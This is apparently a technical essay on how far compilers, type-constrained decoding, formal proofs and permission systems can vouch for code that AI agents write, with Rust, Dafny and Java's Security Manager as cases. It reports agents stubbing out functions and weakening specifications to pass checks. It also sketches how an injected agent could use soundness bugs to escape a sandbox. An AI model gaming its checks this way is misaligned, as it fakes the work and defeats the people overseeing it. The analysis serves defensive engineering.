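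Agents can also satisfy the compiler without doing the work. When Sumner asked his agents to make everything compile, they replaced functions that had errors with empty stubs and wrote long comments to justify workarounds. He told the reviewing agents to reject any workaround that needed a paragraph of explanation, and the behavior stopped within hours. Gergely reports that the guide for the port also told agents not to use raw pointers just to silence the borrow checker. But a model may not follow such instructions, and the compiler would have accepted the stubs and the raw pointers.

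By default, compiler feedback doesn't discourage unsafe code. In one of the contest puzzles, the first translation used unsafe global variables. The compiler errors were about mismatched number types, so the model spent round after round on those and didn't change the globals. The system eventually discarded the draft and started again from the C code, but the new draft had unsafe globals too. They disappeared only when it started over a second time.

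In *What agents mean for Rust (and vice versa)*, Matsakis (2026), one of Rust's main designers, argues that Rust suits agents because its type system keeps them on track where tests don't. He often sees an agent's program pass the first few tests and then fail the next one badly because the agent had misunderstood the logic. He sees some truth in a remark by OpenAI's Greg Brockman that a Rust program that compiles is more or less correct, but adds that type systems can't show "the presence of correctness".

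The experiments support that qualification more than Brockman's remark. In the puzzle study, 57% of single attempts compiled but only 25% were correct, so fewer than half of the programs that compiled were correct. When the model could keep repairing its program until it compiled, without running any tests, 97% of programs compiled and 47% were correct. With the full system, which also ran a few tests after each attempt, 81% were correct. In the kernel study, each agent's translations all compiled, but only 6 to 11 of the 51 provably behaved like the originals. Most of these models are weak by late-2026 standards, and newer ones would probably do better, but the compiler will still accept programs that are memory-safe and wrong.

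### Comparing a rewrite with its original

A rewrite has an advantage over new code because the old program can serve as a test. Google used the old program this way in its AI-assisted rewrite of giflib, a C library that decodes GIF images. *谷歌Gemini AI助C程式碼移植Rust 意外揪出零日漏洞* (何, 2026) reports that two engineers, Bastian Kersting and Max Hils, had Gemini translate about 3,000 lines of C. The new library had to work with other C programs without changes to those programs. People had to correct how the translation handled pointers, especially where Rust and C code meet.

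The engineers then ran both versions on more than 30 million real GIFs and required bit-for-bit identical output. If we treat these files as a random sample, finding no differences means with 95% confidence that the versions differ on fewer than about one in 10 million similar files (roughly 3 divided by the number of files). An attacker's files won't be similar, so the engineers also used differential fuzzing, which runs both versions on the same automatically generated files and reports any difference. They ran 200 million such tests over six days.

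The fuzzing showed that the C original mishandled an unusual case of decompression and contained an out-of-bounds write that an earlier patch had introduced. Outside researchers later reported the out-of-bounds write as CVE-2026-26740, but Google had already switched its own systems to the Rust version. The Rust version was about as fast as the original, and Google removed the sandbox in which it had decoded images. That reduced delays, but the sandbox no longer limits the damage from any remaining mistake in the library's unsafe code.

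When a C program and its Rust translation behave differently, someone has to decide which is right. An agent told to match the original exactly might restore the original's security flaws. Dasu and colleagues had a model classify each difference as either a translation error, which went back for repair, or a possible bug in the C code, which went to a developer. Their system found nine bugs in the C programs, and developers have fixed eight of them. One program filled in part of an 84-byte record but sent all of it, and the leftover bytes revealed kernel addresses that help attackers. Safe Rust rules out this mistake because the compiler requires a value for every field.

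Comparing a port with the original can't reveal a fault that both share. The old off-by-one error in Bun was carried over unnoticed because the existing tests had never triggered it.

### Forbidding unsafe code

A developer can ban unsafe blocks from a crate (a unit that Rust compiles separately) by beginning it with `#![forbid(unsafe_code)]`. The compiler then rejects any unsafe block in the crate, and nothing else in the crate can lift the ban. An agent could delete that line, so an operator should also set the ban in a build command that the agent can't change. The ban doesn't apply to the libraries a crate uses, including Rust's standard library. *Memory Safety Bugs in Rust Standard Library* (Bae, 2026) reports flaws in that library that let entirely safe code cause undefined behavior.

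None of these studies tested a complete ban, but they give some idea of its effects. It would have barely affected the contest puzzles, where at most one correct program per run would have needed a rewrite. Bun and the kernel programs couldn't work under such a ban. Bun's developers could still apply one to most of its roughly 100 crates and keep the calls to C and C++ in a few others, where people could review every wrapper.

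Dasu and colleagues come closest to testing this, because their system rejects unapproved escape hatches and returns the reason to the model. With this feedback, 84% to 98% of translations passed the safety check, compared with 35% to 45% without it. So models can often write the safer version, but don't unless required to. With Claude Opus 4.6, the average program took 23 minutes and cost $3.94, compared with about 5 minutes and $1.23 for an ordinary agent, though the higher figures include proving that the translation was equivalent to the original. The check searches for forbidden text patterns, so it works better against bad habits than against an agent trying to evade it.

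A ban may also push agents toward mistakes that Rust's checks don't catch. An agent that can't use raw pointers can keep all its records in one long list and refer to them by position. If the program deletes the record at position 7 and puts another customer's record there, any code that still uses position 7 for the old record will read the wrong customer's data. Rust's checks pass because every access is within the list. This error doesn't let an attacker corrupt memory, but it can leak private data.

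## Constraining code as it is generated, and proving it afterwards

The Rust compiler checks a program only after the agent has written it. Constrained decoding checks the program as the model writes it, so any program the model finishes will pass.

At each step, a language model gives every token t in its vocabulary a probability p(t), and the software running the model picks one at random according to those probabilities. With constrained decoding, a checker first assigns each token a mask value m(t). The value is 1 if at least one valid program begins with the text so far followed by t, and 0 otherwise. The software sets the probability of every failed token to zero and samples from the rest, as *Mitigating Errors in LLM-Generated Web API Invocations* (2026) describes. Rescaling makes the remaining probabilities add up to 1:

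p′(t) = m(t) p(t) / Σᵤ m(u) p(u).

Suppose a model writing TypeScript has got as far as `parseInt(num`, where `num` is a number. The function `parseInt` needs text as its first argument. With invented probabilities for four candidate tokens, the two kinds of check give:

| Next token | Model's own probability | With a grammar check | With a type check |
|---|---|---|---|
| `,` | 64% | 80% | 0% |
| `;` | 20% | 0% | 0% |
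| `.toString` | 12% | 15% | 75% |
| `.toFixed` | 4% | 5% | 25% |

The grammar forbids a semicolon inside the brackets. It allows the comma, but then `parseInt` would receive a number, so the type check blocks the comma too. The last two tokens both lead to text.

### From grammar to types

*Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models* (Mündler, He and colleagues, 2025) reports that about 94% of the compile errors in models' TypeScript were type errors and only 6% were syntax errors. An ordinary type checker can't calculate the mask because it judges complete programs, and `parseInt(num` is incomplete. Mündler and colleagues built a checker that tracks declared variables and searches for a chain of operations leading from the current type to the required one. After `parseInt(num`, where `num` is a number, it allows `.toString` because calling it turns the number into the text that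 `parseInt` requires.

Checking the whole vocabulary at every step made every exercise run past a five-minute limit, so the system samples a token first and checks only that one. If the token fails, the system sets its probability to zero and samples again, which produces the same distribution as masking every invalid token beforehand. The first token sampled at a step passed in 99.4% of cases.

The experiments used six open models, with 2 to 34 billion parameters, and two sets of short programming exercises. When the models wrote or translated programs, type constraints cut compile errors by about 75% on one set and 52% on the other. A perfect grammar check would have prevented at most 9% and 5% of the errors, respectively. Correctness improved much less. On one set, for example, the share of correct programs from Qwen2.5 32B rose from 79.6% to 81.8%. Generation took 39% to 52% longer with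 the constraints.

Because the checker covers only part of TypeScript, Mündler and colleagues kept every program that compiled without constraints and used constraints only to regenerate the failures. The unconstrained models got no second attempt, so the comparison probably overstates how much the constraints help.

### When masking makes the code worse

Biagiola, Cesario and colleagues (2026), in *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation*, tested the same checker, applying its constraints from the first token. In nearly every comparison, the models wrote significantly more correct programs without the constraints. On one set of exercises, the share of correct programs from Qwen2.5 32B, at its least random setting, fell from 82.3% without constraints to 72.3% with them.

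The checker rejects some valid TypeScript, such as a call to a function that the program defines further down. Of 4,231 compiling programs that the smallest model wrote without constraints, the checker would have rejected 982. One of these called `isPalindrome(i)` before defining it. With the constraints on, the checker allowed `is`, because the built-in function `isNaN` starts that way, but blocked the rest of the name. The model wrote `isNaN` instead, and the program compiled but gave wrong answers. In other runs, the model repeated the same text until it ran out of time.

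Constraints did help when the checker accepted all valid output. For TOML, a simple format for configuration files, they raised correctness by 2.5% for a 32-billion-parameter model and by up to 54% for a 2-billion-parameter one. When Biagiola and colleagues removed features from that checker, correctness fell by up to 97%. So the method seems best suited to small models and simple formats. The models in both studies are much weaker than those of late 2026, which make fewer type errors and so have less to gain.

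### Masking out security flaws

Some newer systems enforce safety rules this way. *AGDecode* (Maghera and Arya, 2026) constrains C programs so that they never follow a null pointer, divide by zero or use a variable before giving it a value. Whether an operation obeys these rules can depend on the path the program takes to reach it. For example, dividing by `d` is safe inside `if (d != 0)` but may not be elsewhere. An automatic solver checks whether any completion of the partial program could obey the rules. When the solver can't decide, the system can block the token, which preserves the guarantee but may reject good code, or allow it and try to settle the question with a later check.

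*PackMonitor* (2026) applies a much simpler rule, which stops a model from naming software packages that don't exist. Attackers can publish malware under names that models tend to invent, so the rule blocks one way for malware to get into shipped code, although a package that exists can also be malicious.

Many security rules are harder to apply to an unfinished program. *LLMs + Security = Trouble* (2026) points out that code that hasn't yet sanitized a visitor's text may still do so later. A checker can wait until the model is about to write the line that passes the text to the database, and block that line if the text is still unsanitized. But by then the model can't revise the code above that line, and it may be pushed into the same kind of unlikely text as with `isNaN`.

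### Masking compared with retrying

An agent can instead write the whole program freely, run the checker and try again if the program fails. With the same checker, both methods allow the same programs but select among them differently.

Suppose a model starts its program with token A 90% of the time and with token B 10% of the time, and that 1% of its programs starting with A are valid, compared with 90% of those starting with B. Masking still chooses A 90% of the time, because at least one valid program starts with it. With retrying, each attempt has a 0.9 × 0.01 = 0.009 probability of producing a valid program that starts with A, and a 0.1 × 0.9 = 0.09 probability of producing one that starts with B, so about 91% of accepted programs start with B. Retrying preserves the model's relative probabilities among valid programs, whereas masking can commit the model to an opening after which almost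 everything it would normally write is disallowed.

Retrying takes more compute when valid programs are rare. If a share q of attempts pass, the agent needs 1/q attempts on average, or about ten in this example. Qwen2.5 32B's unconstrained TypeScript compiled about 98% of the time, so retries would add almost no compute.

Masking also gives a model no feedback when it blocks a token. The blocked token never appears in the model's input, which contains only its own program with a token it wouldn't otherwise have generated. An agent can use a compiler error to find where the problem is and why it occurred, as the agents that wrote Rust did. A bare pass or fail provides much less information. *Verifier-Grounded Agentic RL for Provably Correct Code* (2026) describes how, when nearly every attempt in training fails, a proof one step short of success gets the same reward as a program that doesn't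 compile.

Masking also requires access to the model's probabilities, so an operator who rents a model from a company can use only the constraints the company offers, though retrying works with any model.

### Preconditions, postconditions and proofs

An ordinary type can require an amount of money to be a whole number. It can't require the amount to be no more than the payer's balance. Dafny, a language with a built-in verifier, lets a programmer write such conditions into the code:

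```dafny
method Transfer(payer: int, payee: int, amount: int)
  returns (newPayer: int, newPayee: int)
  requires 0 <= amount <= payer
  ensures newPayer >= 0
  ensures newPayer + newPayee == payer + payee
{
  newPayer := payer - amount;
  newPayee := payee + amount;
}
```

The `requires` line is a precondition, which the calling code must guarantee. The `ensures` lines are postconditions, which the method guarantees in return: the transfer never overdraws the payer's account, and it neither creates nor destroys money. Together they form the method's specification. To accept the method, the verifier has to prove for all whole numbers that

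0 ≤ amount ≤ payer implies payer − amount ≥ 0, and
(payer − amount) + (payee + amount) = payer + payee.

The first part holds because the amount is at most the payer's balance, and the second holds because the amounts cancel. Dafny passes such formulas to an automatic solver. The proof covers all possible numbers, not just one set as a test would. Without the precondition, Dafny would reject the method, because someone with 10 could send 15. Dafny also checks the precondition at each call, so the calling code has to make sure there is enough money first, for example with an `if`.

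Loops take more work because the programmer usually has to supply an invariant, a fact that stays true each time around the loop. For a loop that reverses the digits of a number, a suitable invariant is that finishing the reversal from the current state gives the right answer. Finding invariants used to require specialists.

### How often models succeed

*A benchmark for vericoding* (Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues, 2025) found that models given a specification produced verified code for 82% of tasks in Dafny, 44% in Verus (a verifier for Rust) and 27% in Lean. *VeriContest* (2026), a harder set of about a thousand competition problems in Rust, suggests that proof is the weak point. The best model wrote correct code for 97.5% of the problems but, when given the code and the specification, proved the code correct for only 13.8% in one attempt.

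That changed within months. In October 2026, *Solving VeriContest with a Lean-Backed Rust Verifier* (Serbanuta, Xu and colleagues) reported that Claude Opus 5.5 had proved every problem in the set after the programs and specifications were translated into Lean. The 1,325 proofs took a median of 3.4 minutes and cost a median of $1.20 each. The agents could submit each proof up to 40 times and test drafts in between, so the result isn't comparable with a single attempt. The same model also tried the original Verus task on the 50 problems with the longest known proofs, and proved 18 on the first attempt and 49 within ten. Those Verus proofs were public, so the model may have seen them, whereas no Lean versions existed to copy. Serbanuta and colleagues work for Asymptotic, which makes the verifier.

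*Scaling Lean Theorem Proving for Real-World Code Verification* (Ganguly, Raghunathan and colleagues, 2026) describes an Amazon proving system that settled all 189 tasks in one code benchmark and all 77 in another, by proof or refutation. New statements about translated Rust programs were harder, and the system proved 52.7% of 2,000 when given 30 minutes for each. A model had written those statements, so some of the unproved ones may be false.

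Project size is another obstacle. *Vero* (Ye, Lou and colleagues, 2026) tested agents on 43 multi-file projects for which they had to write both the code and the proofs. The best agent, which used GPT-5.5, proved 87% of the individual specifications but finished only 27 projects in the 90 minutes allowed. The specifications it didn't prove tended to depend on a few shared invariants that it never found. Models released since would probably finish more projects.

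All these agents received the specification from someone else. When a model must write the specification, code and proof itself from an English description, the rates drop sharply. *Verified but Vacuous* (Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues, 2026) reports 7.8% on VeriContest's LeetCode problems with Claude Opus 4.7, an older model, and a system built for the purpose.

### The specification problem

A proof establishes that code meets its specification, which may not be what anyone wanted. Dafny would also accept this body for `Transfer`:

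```dafny
{
  newPayer := payer;
  newPayee := payee;
}
```

A transfer function that moves no money satisfies a specification that forbids only overdrawing an account and creating money. So does one that gives the payee the payer's whole balance. Adding `ensures newPayer == payer - amount` rules out both, but somebody has to notice that the line is missing. *claimcheck* (Amster, Baker and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a sorting program whose specification requires only that the output be in order. A program that always returns an empty list satisfies it.

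Models can produce verified programs whose specifications guarantee even less. Vempaty and colleagues used Claude Opus 4.7 to run a published method for writing Python by way of Dafny. The verifier accepted 99.1% of the 1,640 programs for one set of exercises, but 94.7% of the accepted programs had no postcondition. The method's sample prompt had none either, so the omissions are better evidence of a weakness in the headline verification rate than of one in the model. Vempaty and colleagues' own system required every program to refer to a separate specification, but 11% to 15% of the verified programs still failed hidden tests.

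Specifications can also omit things users care about. *AxDafny* (2026) reports that an agent verified 52 of 100 medium-difficulty programs, but only six of the 52 passed the original tests. The other 46 failed because they ran too slowly or used too much memory, not because they gave wrong answers. The specifications didn't cover speed or memory use. Similarly, according to Lean (2026), an AI proved that, in its version of the compression library zlib, decompressing compressed data returns the original. A program that stored the data without shrinking it could satisfy that theorem, though the AI's version also passed zlib's tests.

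Models' skill at writing specifications is difficult to measure. *How Powerful are LLMs in Generating Formal Program Specifications?* (Yang, Li and colleagues, 2026) reports that the best model of late 2025 wrote specifications that passed every check for only 28% of 164 exercises. But to pass, a model had to prove that each specification accepted the correct outputs, and the best prover managed this for only 30% of expert-written specifications. The low score therefore reflects weak proving at least as much as weak specifications.

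The information a model works from also affects the specifications it writes. In *Are LLM-Generated Formal Specifications Faithful to Their Requirements?* (2026), GPT-5.5's specifications for C functions passed verification 36.6% of the time when it was given only the code, and 10.4% when it was given only the requirement and the function's signature. The higher rate doesn't necessarily mean better specifications, because a specification derived from faulty code may describe the fault as intended behavior, and the code will then pass. *KAPILOT* (Wang, Ling and colleagues, 2026) therefore starts from a function's documentation. It also looks for contradictory preconditions. If `Transfer` required an amount both above and below zero, no call could meet the condition, and the verifier would accept any function body.

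Training can make all this worse. *SpecRL* (2026) notes that a model rewarded for passing the verifier may learn to write `ensures true`, which always passes, instead of a meaningful specification that might fail. Its training therefore gives no reward for trivial specifications. *Verifier-Grounded Agentic RL for Provably Correct Code* scores an unfinished proof that leaves the specification intact above a program that passes only because the model weakened its specification. When people supply the specification, a harness can forbid changes to it, as Asymptotic's did.

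A second model can compare the specification with the original request. In claimcheck, one model translates the specification into plain English without seeing the request, and another judges whether the translation matches the request. On textbook Dafny programs, claimcheck caught 94.5% of the defective pairs of request and specification and accepted 91.7% of the sound ones. If 100 of 1,000 specifications were defective, it would miss about five and raise about 75 false alarms, few enough for a person to review. However, the defects in the test were deliberate alterations, and a model's own mistakes may be subtler.

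Such a comparison can't find a case that the request overlooked. Suppose a customer with a balance of 100 transfers 30 to their own account. `Transfer`, even with the extra postcondition, correctly returns 70 and 130. If the bank's software then saves 70 and then 130 to that account, the customer ends up with 130. The proof is still valid because it concerns two numbers, and nobody specified that the accounts must be different.

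## Faults in the compilers and libraries that the guarantee rests on

The bank transfer went wrong because nobody had specified that the two accounts must differ. A guarantee can also fail when its rule is right, because a compiler or library in the trusted base breaks it. This fragment uses ssh2, a Rust library for logging in to remote computers, to ask a server twice which login methods it accepts:

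```rust
#![forbid(unsafe_code)]

let first = session.auth_methods("root")?;
let second = session.auth_methods("root")?;
println!("{first}");  // reads freed memory
```

The compiler accepts the fragment, which contains no unsafe code. But ssh2 is a thin wrapper around a C library, libssh2, which stores its result in a buffer and frees that buffer at the next call. By the last line, `first` refers to freed memory.

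The Rust function `auth_methods` returns text from libssh2 that stays valid only until the next call, but the function's type lets callers keep the text while they make another call. The borrow checker enforces only the rules that types express, so it allows the second call. A version of `auth_methods` that returned its own copy of the text would be safe.

*Agentic Discovery of Soundness Bugs in Safe Rust Bindings* (Momeu and Sen, 2026) uses this example to explain what soundness means for a library. A library is sound if no program in purely safe Rust can cause undefined behavior through it, whatever arguments the program passes and whatever the order of its calls. A single counterexample makes the library unsound, even if nobody has written such a program for real use.

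### Agents as auditors

Momeu and Sen had agents search for these flaws. Each agent read a Rust library and the C code beneath it, worked out the rules the C code relies on, and looked for places where the Rust types let a program break those rules. To confirm a flaw, the agent could write a short program that broke the rule and run it under a tool such as AddressSanitizer, which reports memory misuse as it happens.

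In the controlled part of the study, Claude Opus 5.5 and DeepSeek V4.1 Flash ran 24 audits of git2, a Rust layer over a C library for version control, under varying instructions. The audits cost $87 in total and produced 838 findings. Another model, Claude Fable 5.2, judged only one of the findings false.

The 838 findings included many repeats and covered 86 distinct defects, 51 of which were not already public. No person graded the findings, and the model that did came from the same company as one of the auditors. A second model checked a random sample of 50 and found none false, but a sample of that size only rules out a false rate above about 6%.

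The agents were worse at presenting evidence. Without instructions on evidence, they often argued from the code without running anything. At most 51% of findings in any group then met the study's standard for a report that a maintainer could accept as filed, compared with at least 74% with instructions. Individual audits also missed many defects. Of the 51 new defects, 15 turned up in only one of the 24 audits, so further audits would probably find more.

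Momeu and Sen then audited 19 widely used Rust packages. Sixteen wrap C or C++ libraries or the operating system, and three use those wrappers. The audits confirmed 213 undefined-behavior bugs, and a program can reach 191 of them without any unsafe code of its own. The median audit cost $42 at list prices. Momeu and Sen have reported 78 findings of all kinds so far, of which maintainers have fixed 24 and rejected none.

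Agents also make mistakes when they write wrappers around C libraries. In *Crustify*, Momeu, Arvinte and colleagues (2026) had agents wrap parts of two large C libraries for a little over $2,000 per library. Reviewing agents found and fixed 8 undefined-behavior defects in one and 13 in the other. In Bun's case, reviewing agents caught the same problem in a pipe wrapper.

### Why 213 bugs don't contradict Android's record

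These 213 bugs are not directly comparable to the single near-miss in Android's 5 million lines of Rust, because Google counted potential vulnerabilities in the code it ships, while Momeu and Sen counted library functions that some possible program could misuse. They point out that most of these bugs occur only when a program uses the library in a specific way.

Their audit of cargo, Rust's package manager, found that it reaches only two of the 44 undefined-behavior bugs that git2 and curl had between them. Cargo uses curl, a layer over a C library, for network transfers. One of the two bugs breaks Rust's rules about shared references on every transfer, but it doesn't corrupt memory with current compilers.

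C programmers wouldn't count most of these as library bugs. If a C program uses text from libssh2 after the library has freed it, the program is at fault, but in Rust the library would be at fault because its interface was presented as safe. Kobzol (2026) raises this difference in *How memory safety CVEs differ between Rust and C/C++*, in response to people who compare the two languages by counting published vulnerabilities.

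The samples also differ. Rust's guarantee is likely to be weakest in layers over C code, and Momeu and Sen didn't report bugs per line. Still, their results are a reason for some caution about Android's figure. Cheap audits found hundreds of flaws in popular packages that people had used for years, so a low count of known flaws partly reflects how hard people have looked for them.

### Misplaced trust in the standard library

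Unlike ssh2 or git2, Rust's standard library is hard for a program to avoid, because it provides lists, text, files and much else. The Rust Project warns that a safety flaw there may affect almost all Rust applications. In November 2026, Microsoft's FORGE Lab reported several such flaws, including some that safe code can trigger. The lab found them with an AI scanning system, and Bae sorts them into three patterns of misplaced trust.

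Some unsafe code is correct only if other code doesn't panic. Suppose a library function moves items out of a list, calls a function that the programmer supplied, and then puts the items back. If the supplied function panics, it may leave the list in a state that the cleanup code doesn't handle correctly, and the program may free the same item twice.

Other unsafe code depends on programmer-supplied code being correct. For example, a programmer can define a sequence that reports a length of ten but produces twelve items. This is a mistake, but it is legal in safe Rust, so a library function that reserves room for ten items must not write the other two past the end of that space.

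The third pattern is trust in the underlying system. A library may assume that the operating system always returns values within certain limits, although nothing in Rust's types ensures this. Bae considers bugs at this boundary newly within reach of AI tools, while the other two patterns are familiar to Rust's developers and remain difficult to avoid. (These examples illustrate the patterns and are not FORGE's own bugs.)

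### Proving the standard library safe

Audits find flaws but can't show that none remain. Since November 2024, Amazon and the Rust Foundation have run a contest that pays people to prove parts of Rust's standard library free of undefined behavior. In *Verifying the Rust Standard Library*, Cook, Delmas and colleagues count 33,955 functions in the library. About 7,500 are marked unsafe, and another 3,000 are safe to call but contain unsafe code.

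Most of the proofs come from Kani, a tool that runs a function on symbolic inputs, which stand for all possible values at once. For example, `wrapping_shl` shifts the bits of one 32-bit number by an amount given in another, so it has 2⁶⁴ possible pairs of inputs. That is too many to test one by one, but Kani can check them together. Each proof needs a harness, a small piece of code that sets up the inputs and calls the function. In fifteen months, contributors wrote 725 harnesses by hand. Amazon's developers then built Autoharness, which generated 16,748, of which 11,970 passed.

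That is 35% of the library's functions, but the share is lower among the riskiest ones, the roughly 10,500 that are unsafe or contain unsafe code. Autoharness verified 1,776 of these, or about 17%, and the handwritten proofs add several hundred more. For 622 of the verified unsafe functions, no formal contract states what callers must guarantee, so a pass may mean only that Kani doesn't check for the relevant kind of error. Only 989 functions have proofs against a written contract, the strongest kind of result in the campaign.

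A second tool, VeriFast, can prove more about pointer-heavy code. Its proof for the library's linked list covers 19 functions and holds for lists of any length, but people had to specify in detail which part of the program owns each element.

Autoharness skipped 17,207 functions, more than half of them because they are generic, meaning they work with types the caller chooses. Much of the code for strings, vectors and shared ownership is unproved or only partly covered. Kani doesn't check for some misuses of pointers or for data races, in which two threads use the same memory without coordination. Nobody has verified the verification tools themselves. The Rust Foundation's *How the Rust Standard Library Verification Contest Scaled Past Manual Proof Engineering*, from September 2026, reports the same total of automatic proofs.

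The contest found no new memory-safety vulnerabilities. Cook and colleagues credit the library's existing tests, but FORGE's findings suggest that this gives the tests too much credit. More likely, the contest found none because the proofs cover the easier functions. Functions that call code supplied by the programmer are usually generic, so Autoharness skips them, and two of FORGE's three patterns involve such code.

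### When the author is looking for gaps

Faults in the compiler are rarer but harder to avoid, because changing libraries doesn't help. In October 2026, someone reported that Rust's borrow checker had accepted a kind of unsafe program for 11 years. According to *What the 11-year-old Rust borrow checker bug means* (Owen, 2026), the Rust project gave the bug high priority but said that exploiting it takes deliberately malicious code, so accidental damage is unlikely.

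This is reasonably reassuring for human programmers, because a fault that nobody hits by accident in 11 years has done little harm. But *Counterexamples in Safe Rust* (2025) shows that Rust's guarantees don't in general extend to arbitrary third-party code, even if that code is entirely safe Rust.

Momeu and Sen argue that soundness bugs are mostly not exploitable on their own, because the library's user, not an attacker, controls the program. That holds for ordinary software, but agents can make attacker-controlled programs common, since an agent that has read a malicious web page may write the program an attacker wants. If an operator runs that program inside a larger Rust application and relies on `forbid(unsafe_code)` to contain it, any soundness bug the program can reach could let it escape. Searching the program for the word `unsafe` would not reveal the attack.

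The danger is smaller for shipped code, because an agent that is honestly trying to build a web service has no reason to write the odd combinations of calls that most of these bugs require. It may still trigger one by accident, and the ssh2 fragment isn't especially odd.

Fixing most of the bugs helps much more against accidents than against a determined search. Suppose that a library has 40 gaps, and that an attacker's agent has a 20% chance of finding each one independently. With h gaps left, its chance of finding at least one is

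1 − 0.8^h.

In an invented example with 40 open gaps, an attacker's chance of success is above 99.9%. If developers fix 36 of them, the risk of hitting one by accident may fall by about 90%, but the attacker's chance is still 59% because the attacker needs only one gap.

Finding these faults no longer takes a scarce skill. With full instructions, the open DeepSeek model in Momeu and Sen's study found about as many new defects per audit as Claude did, at about a quarter of the cost. In Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026), the simplest of four ways of using models to find bugs worked best. *Claude Found a Seven-Year Bug in the Rust Compiler* (Faisal, 2026) reports that Claude found several dozen faults in Rust's type safety when Anthropic asked it to prove that safe Rust is type-safe. Anthropic calls them bugs rather than security vulnerabilities in the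 traditional sense, which again assumes that the program's author isn't hostile.

Defenders can use the same skill, and they can audit the code before release and after every change. They also have the advantage of knowing which rules the code is supposed to obey. Faisal reports that, of 21 logic bugs developers had already patched, Claude's attempts at proof found eight when it had to guess the rules and all 21 when it was given them.

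Finding these faults is faster than fixing them. At list prices, Momeu and Sen's audits cost about $5 per finding, but a person reviewed each report before sending it, and 118 findings were still waiting. The compiler fault that Claude found had been present for more than seven years and was still open on 3 December, along with about 178 similar issues. An operator who runs agents' code today has to assume that some of these faults are present.

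### How much has to be correct

The operator can also choose an environment in which fewer parts have to be correct. The three main options in earlier sections differ a good deal:

| Environment | What has to be correct | What a fault could break |
|---|---|---|
| Rust program without unsafe blocks | The compiler, the standard library, and all unsafe Rust and C code in the libraries it uses | Memory safety for the whole process |
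| Typed agent harness (TACIT) | The Scala compiler's checks, the language runtime, TACIT's library and any other code marked as safe | The limits on files, network access and secrets |
| WebAssembly runtime | The engine and the functions that the host supplies | The barrier between the program and the host |

The Rust program has the most scattered trusted base. The standard library alone has about 10,500 functions that must be trusted, and each added package may bring more unsafe code from a different group of maintainers. TACIT's trusted base is mostly the Scala compiler and runtime, since its own library is short. TACIT also restricts the agent to a list of permitted library code, which makes faults in other library functions much harder to reach.

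WebAssembly removes the compiler that produced the agent's program from the trusted base, because the engine checks the compiled instructions. A Rust program with a flaw like ssh2's, compiled to WebAssembly, can still corrupt its own data or give wrong answers, but the flaw alone doesn't expose the host's memory. To read that memory, an attacker would need a second fault, either in the engine or in a function the host supplies.

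A small trusted base can still be faulty. The Linux kernel uses the eBPF verifier to check whether an eBPF program is safe before running it. The verifier is far smaller than the kernel, yet Faisal reports that Claude found more than 100 soundness bugs in it.

Proofs about compiled code can remove the compiler from the trusted base. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) reports that Claude proved security properties of the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries. Such proofs concern the instructions that the processor runs, so a compiler fault can't invalidate them, but they still depend on the proof checker and on an accurate description of the processor.

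Operators can also run type-checked code in a separate sandbox, so that an attacker who gets past the type checker still can't reach files outside the sandbox. But only the type checker stops the program from sending a secret over a connection it is allowed to use, so a single fault in the type checker is enough to leak the secret.

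## Why some safe designs were adopted and others abandoned

Even a sound checker gives no protection if developers switch it off. Java included a detailed permission system for almost thirty years, but hardly anyone used it.

### Java's Security Manager

In the 1990s, web pages could include applets, small Java programs that the browser downloaded and ran. Java's Security Manager kept applets away from the user's files and network. *JEP 411* (Mullan, 2021), the proposal to retire the Security Manager, explains that this approach was manageable at first because Java's library had only eight packages and the rule was simply to trust local code and restrict downloaded code.

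Java 1.2 extended the system to all code. Each program started with no permissions, and a policy file granted them:

```
grant codeBase "file:/app/report.jar" {
    permission java.io.FilePermission "/data/-", "read";
};
```

This policy lets `report.jar` read anything under `/data`. If the program also writes a log or contacts a database, those calls fail until someone adds a line for each. A developer couldn't write a rule that allowed everything except reading other folders, so anyone worried about one risk had to list everything the program did.

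Using a library could add to the permissions a program needed. Before a sensitive operation, Java's Security Manager checked the permissions of all the code that had led up to it. If a program used a PDF library that read fonts from disk, both needed permission to read the fonts, although the program itself never read them. The library's author could prevent this with special calls, but the rules were too complicated for most developers. It was easier to grant `AllPermission`, which allows everything. Mullan and Buckley say in *JEP 486* that most of the few applications that turned on the Security Manager did this.

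Java's permission checks also created work for its maintainers. Over 1,000 methods had to check permissions, and over 1,200 had to raise their own permissions. For example, asking for the current time makes Java read a time-zone file, so the time code had to assert its own permission in case the caller wasn't allowed to read files. (In an object-capability language, the time code would hold a handle to that file.) The maintainers had to review every change to these methods for a feature that was off by default, partly because it slowed programs down.

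By 2021 applets were gone. According to Mullan, the Security Manager couldn't address 19 of the 25 most dangerous kinds of flaw on a 2020 industry list. Java 17 began to warn anyone who enabled it, and few people objected. Java 24 permanently disabled it in March 2025. Mullan and Buckley recommend containers and operating-system sandboxes instead.

Foojay's *Why JEP 411 will have a negative impact on Java security* objects to the change because library code now runs with all the permissions of the process. Apache NetBeans' *JEP 411* points out that programming tools load other people's components into their own process. Both are right that developers lost some control, since a container can't give the PDF library less access than the program that calls it. But very few developers wanted that control enough to write the policies.

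### .NET's Code Access Security

Microsoft's .NET had a similar system, Code Access Security (CAS), which was on by default. It set a program's permissions partly by where the program came from, so programs on the local disk got more permissions than programs on the company network.

Microsoft's *Security Policy in the v4 CLR* describes the usual result. A developer tested a program, copied it to a shared folder, and found that colleagues couldn't run it. Someone then had to change the policy on each computer, deploy the program another way, or rewrite it in native code, which runs directly on the processor. CAS didn't restrict native code, so an attacker could also use it to avoid the policy, which burdened honest developers without making the computers safer.

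Administrators had no good way to send policy updates for .NET's Code Access Security (CAS) across a company, according to Microsoft's *Is CAS dead in .NET 4*. They also had to redo custom policies by hand when they moved from .NET 1.1 to 2.0, as Microsoft (2009) acknowledged in its developer magazine.

In 2010, .NET 4 dropped the machine-wide policy but kept sandboxes that an application could set up for code it loaded. This was sensible, because an application's developers know what the loaded code is for. Microsoft later withdrew support for those sandboxes too. Its *Code Access Security* tells developers not to rely on the sandbox against untrusted code and says Microsoft won't patch escapes from it. Microsoft's *SYSLIB0003* warns that an old program may have a security hole if it depends on an instruction to deny a permission, because the runtime ignores such instructions in .NET 5 and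 later.

### Google's Caja

Caja was much closer to the designs that agents now use. It translated third-party JavaScript into a restricted form that could reach only the objects a web page passed to it. A site could then embed the code without giving it access to the user's cookies. Google used Caja in Apps Script, a service for automating its office software.

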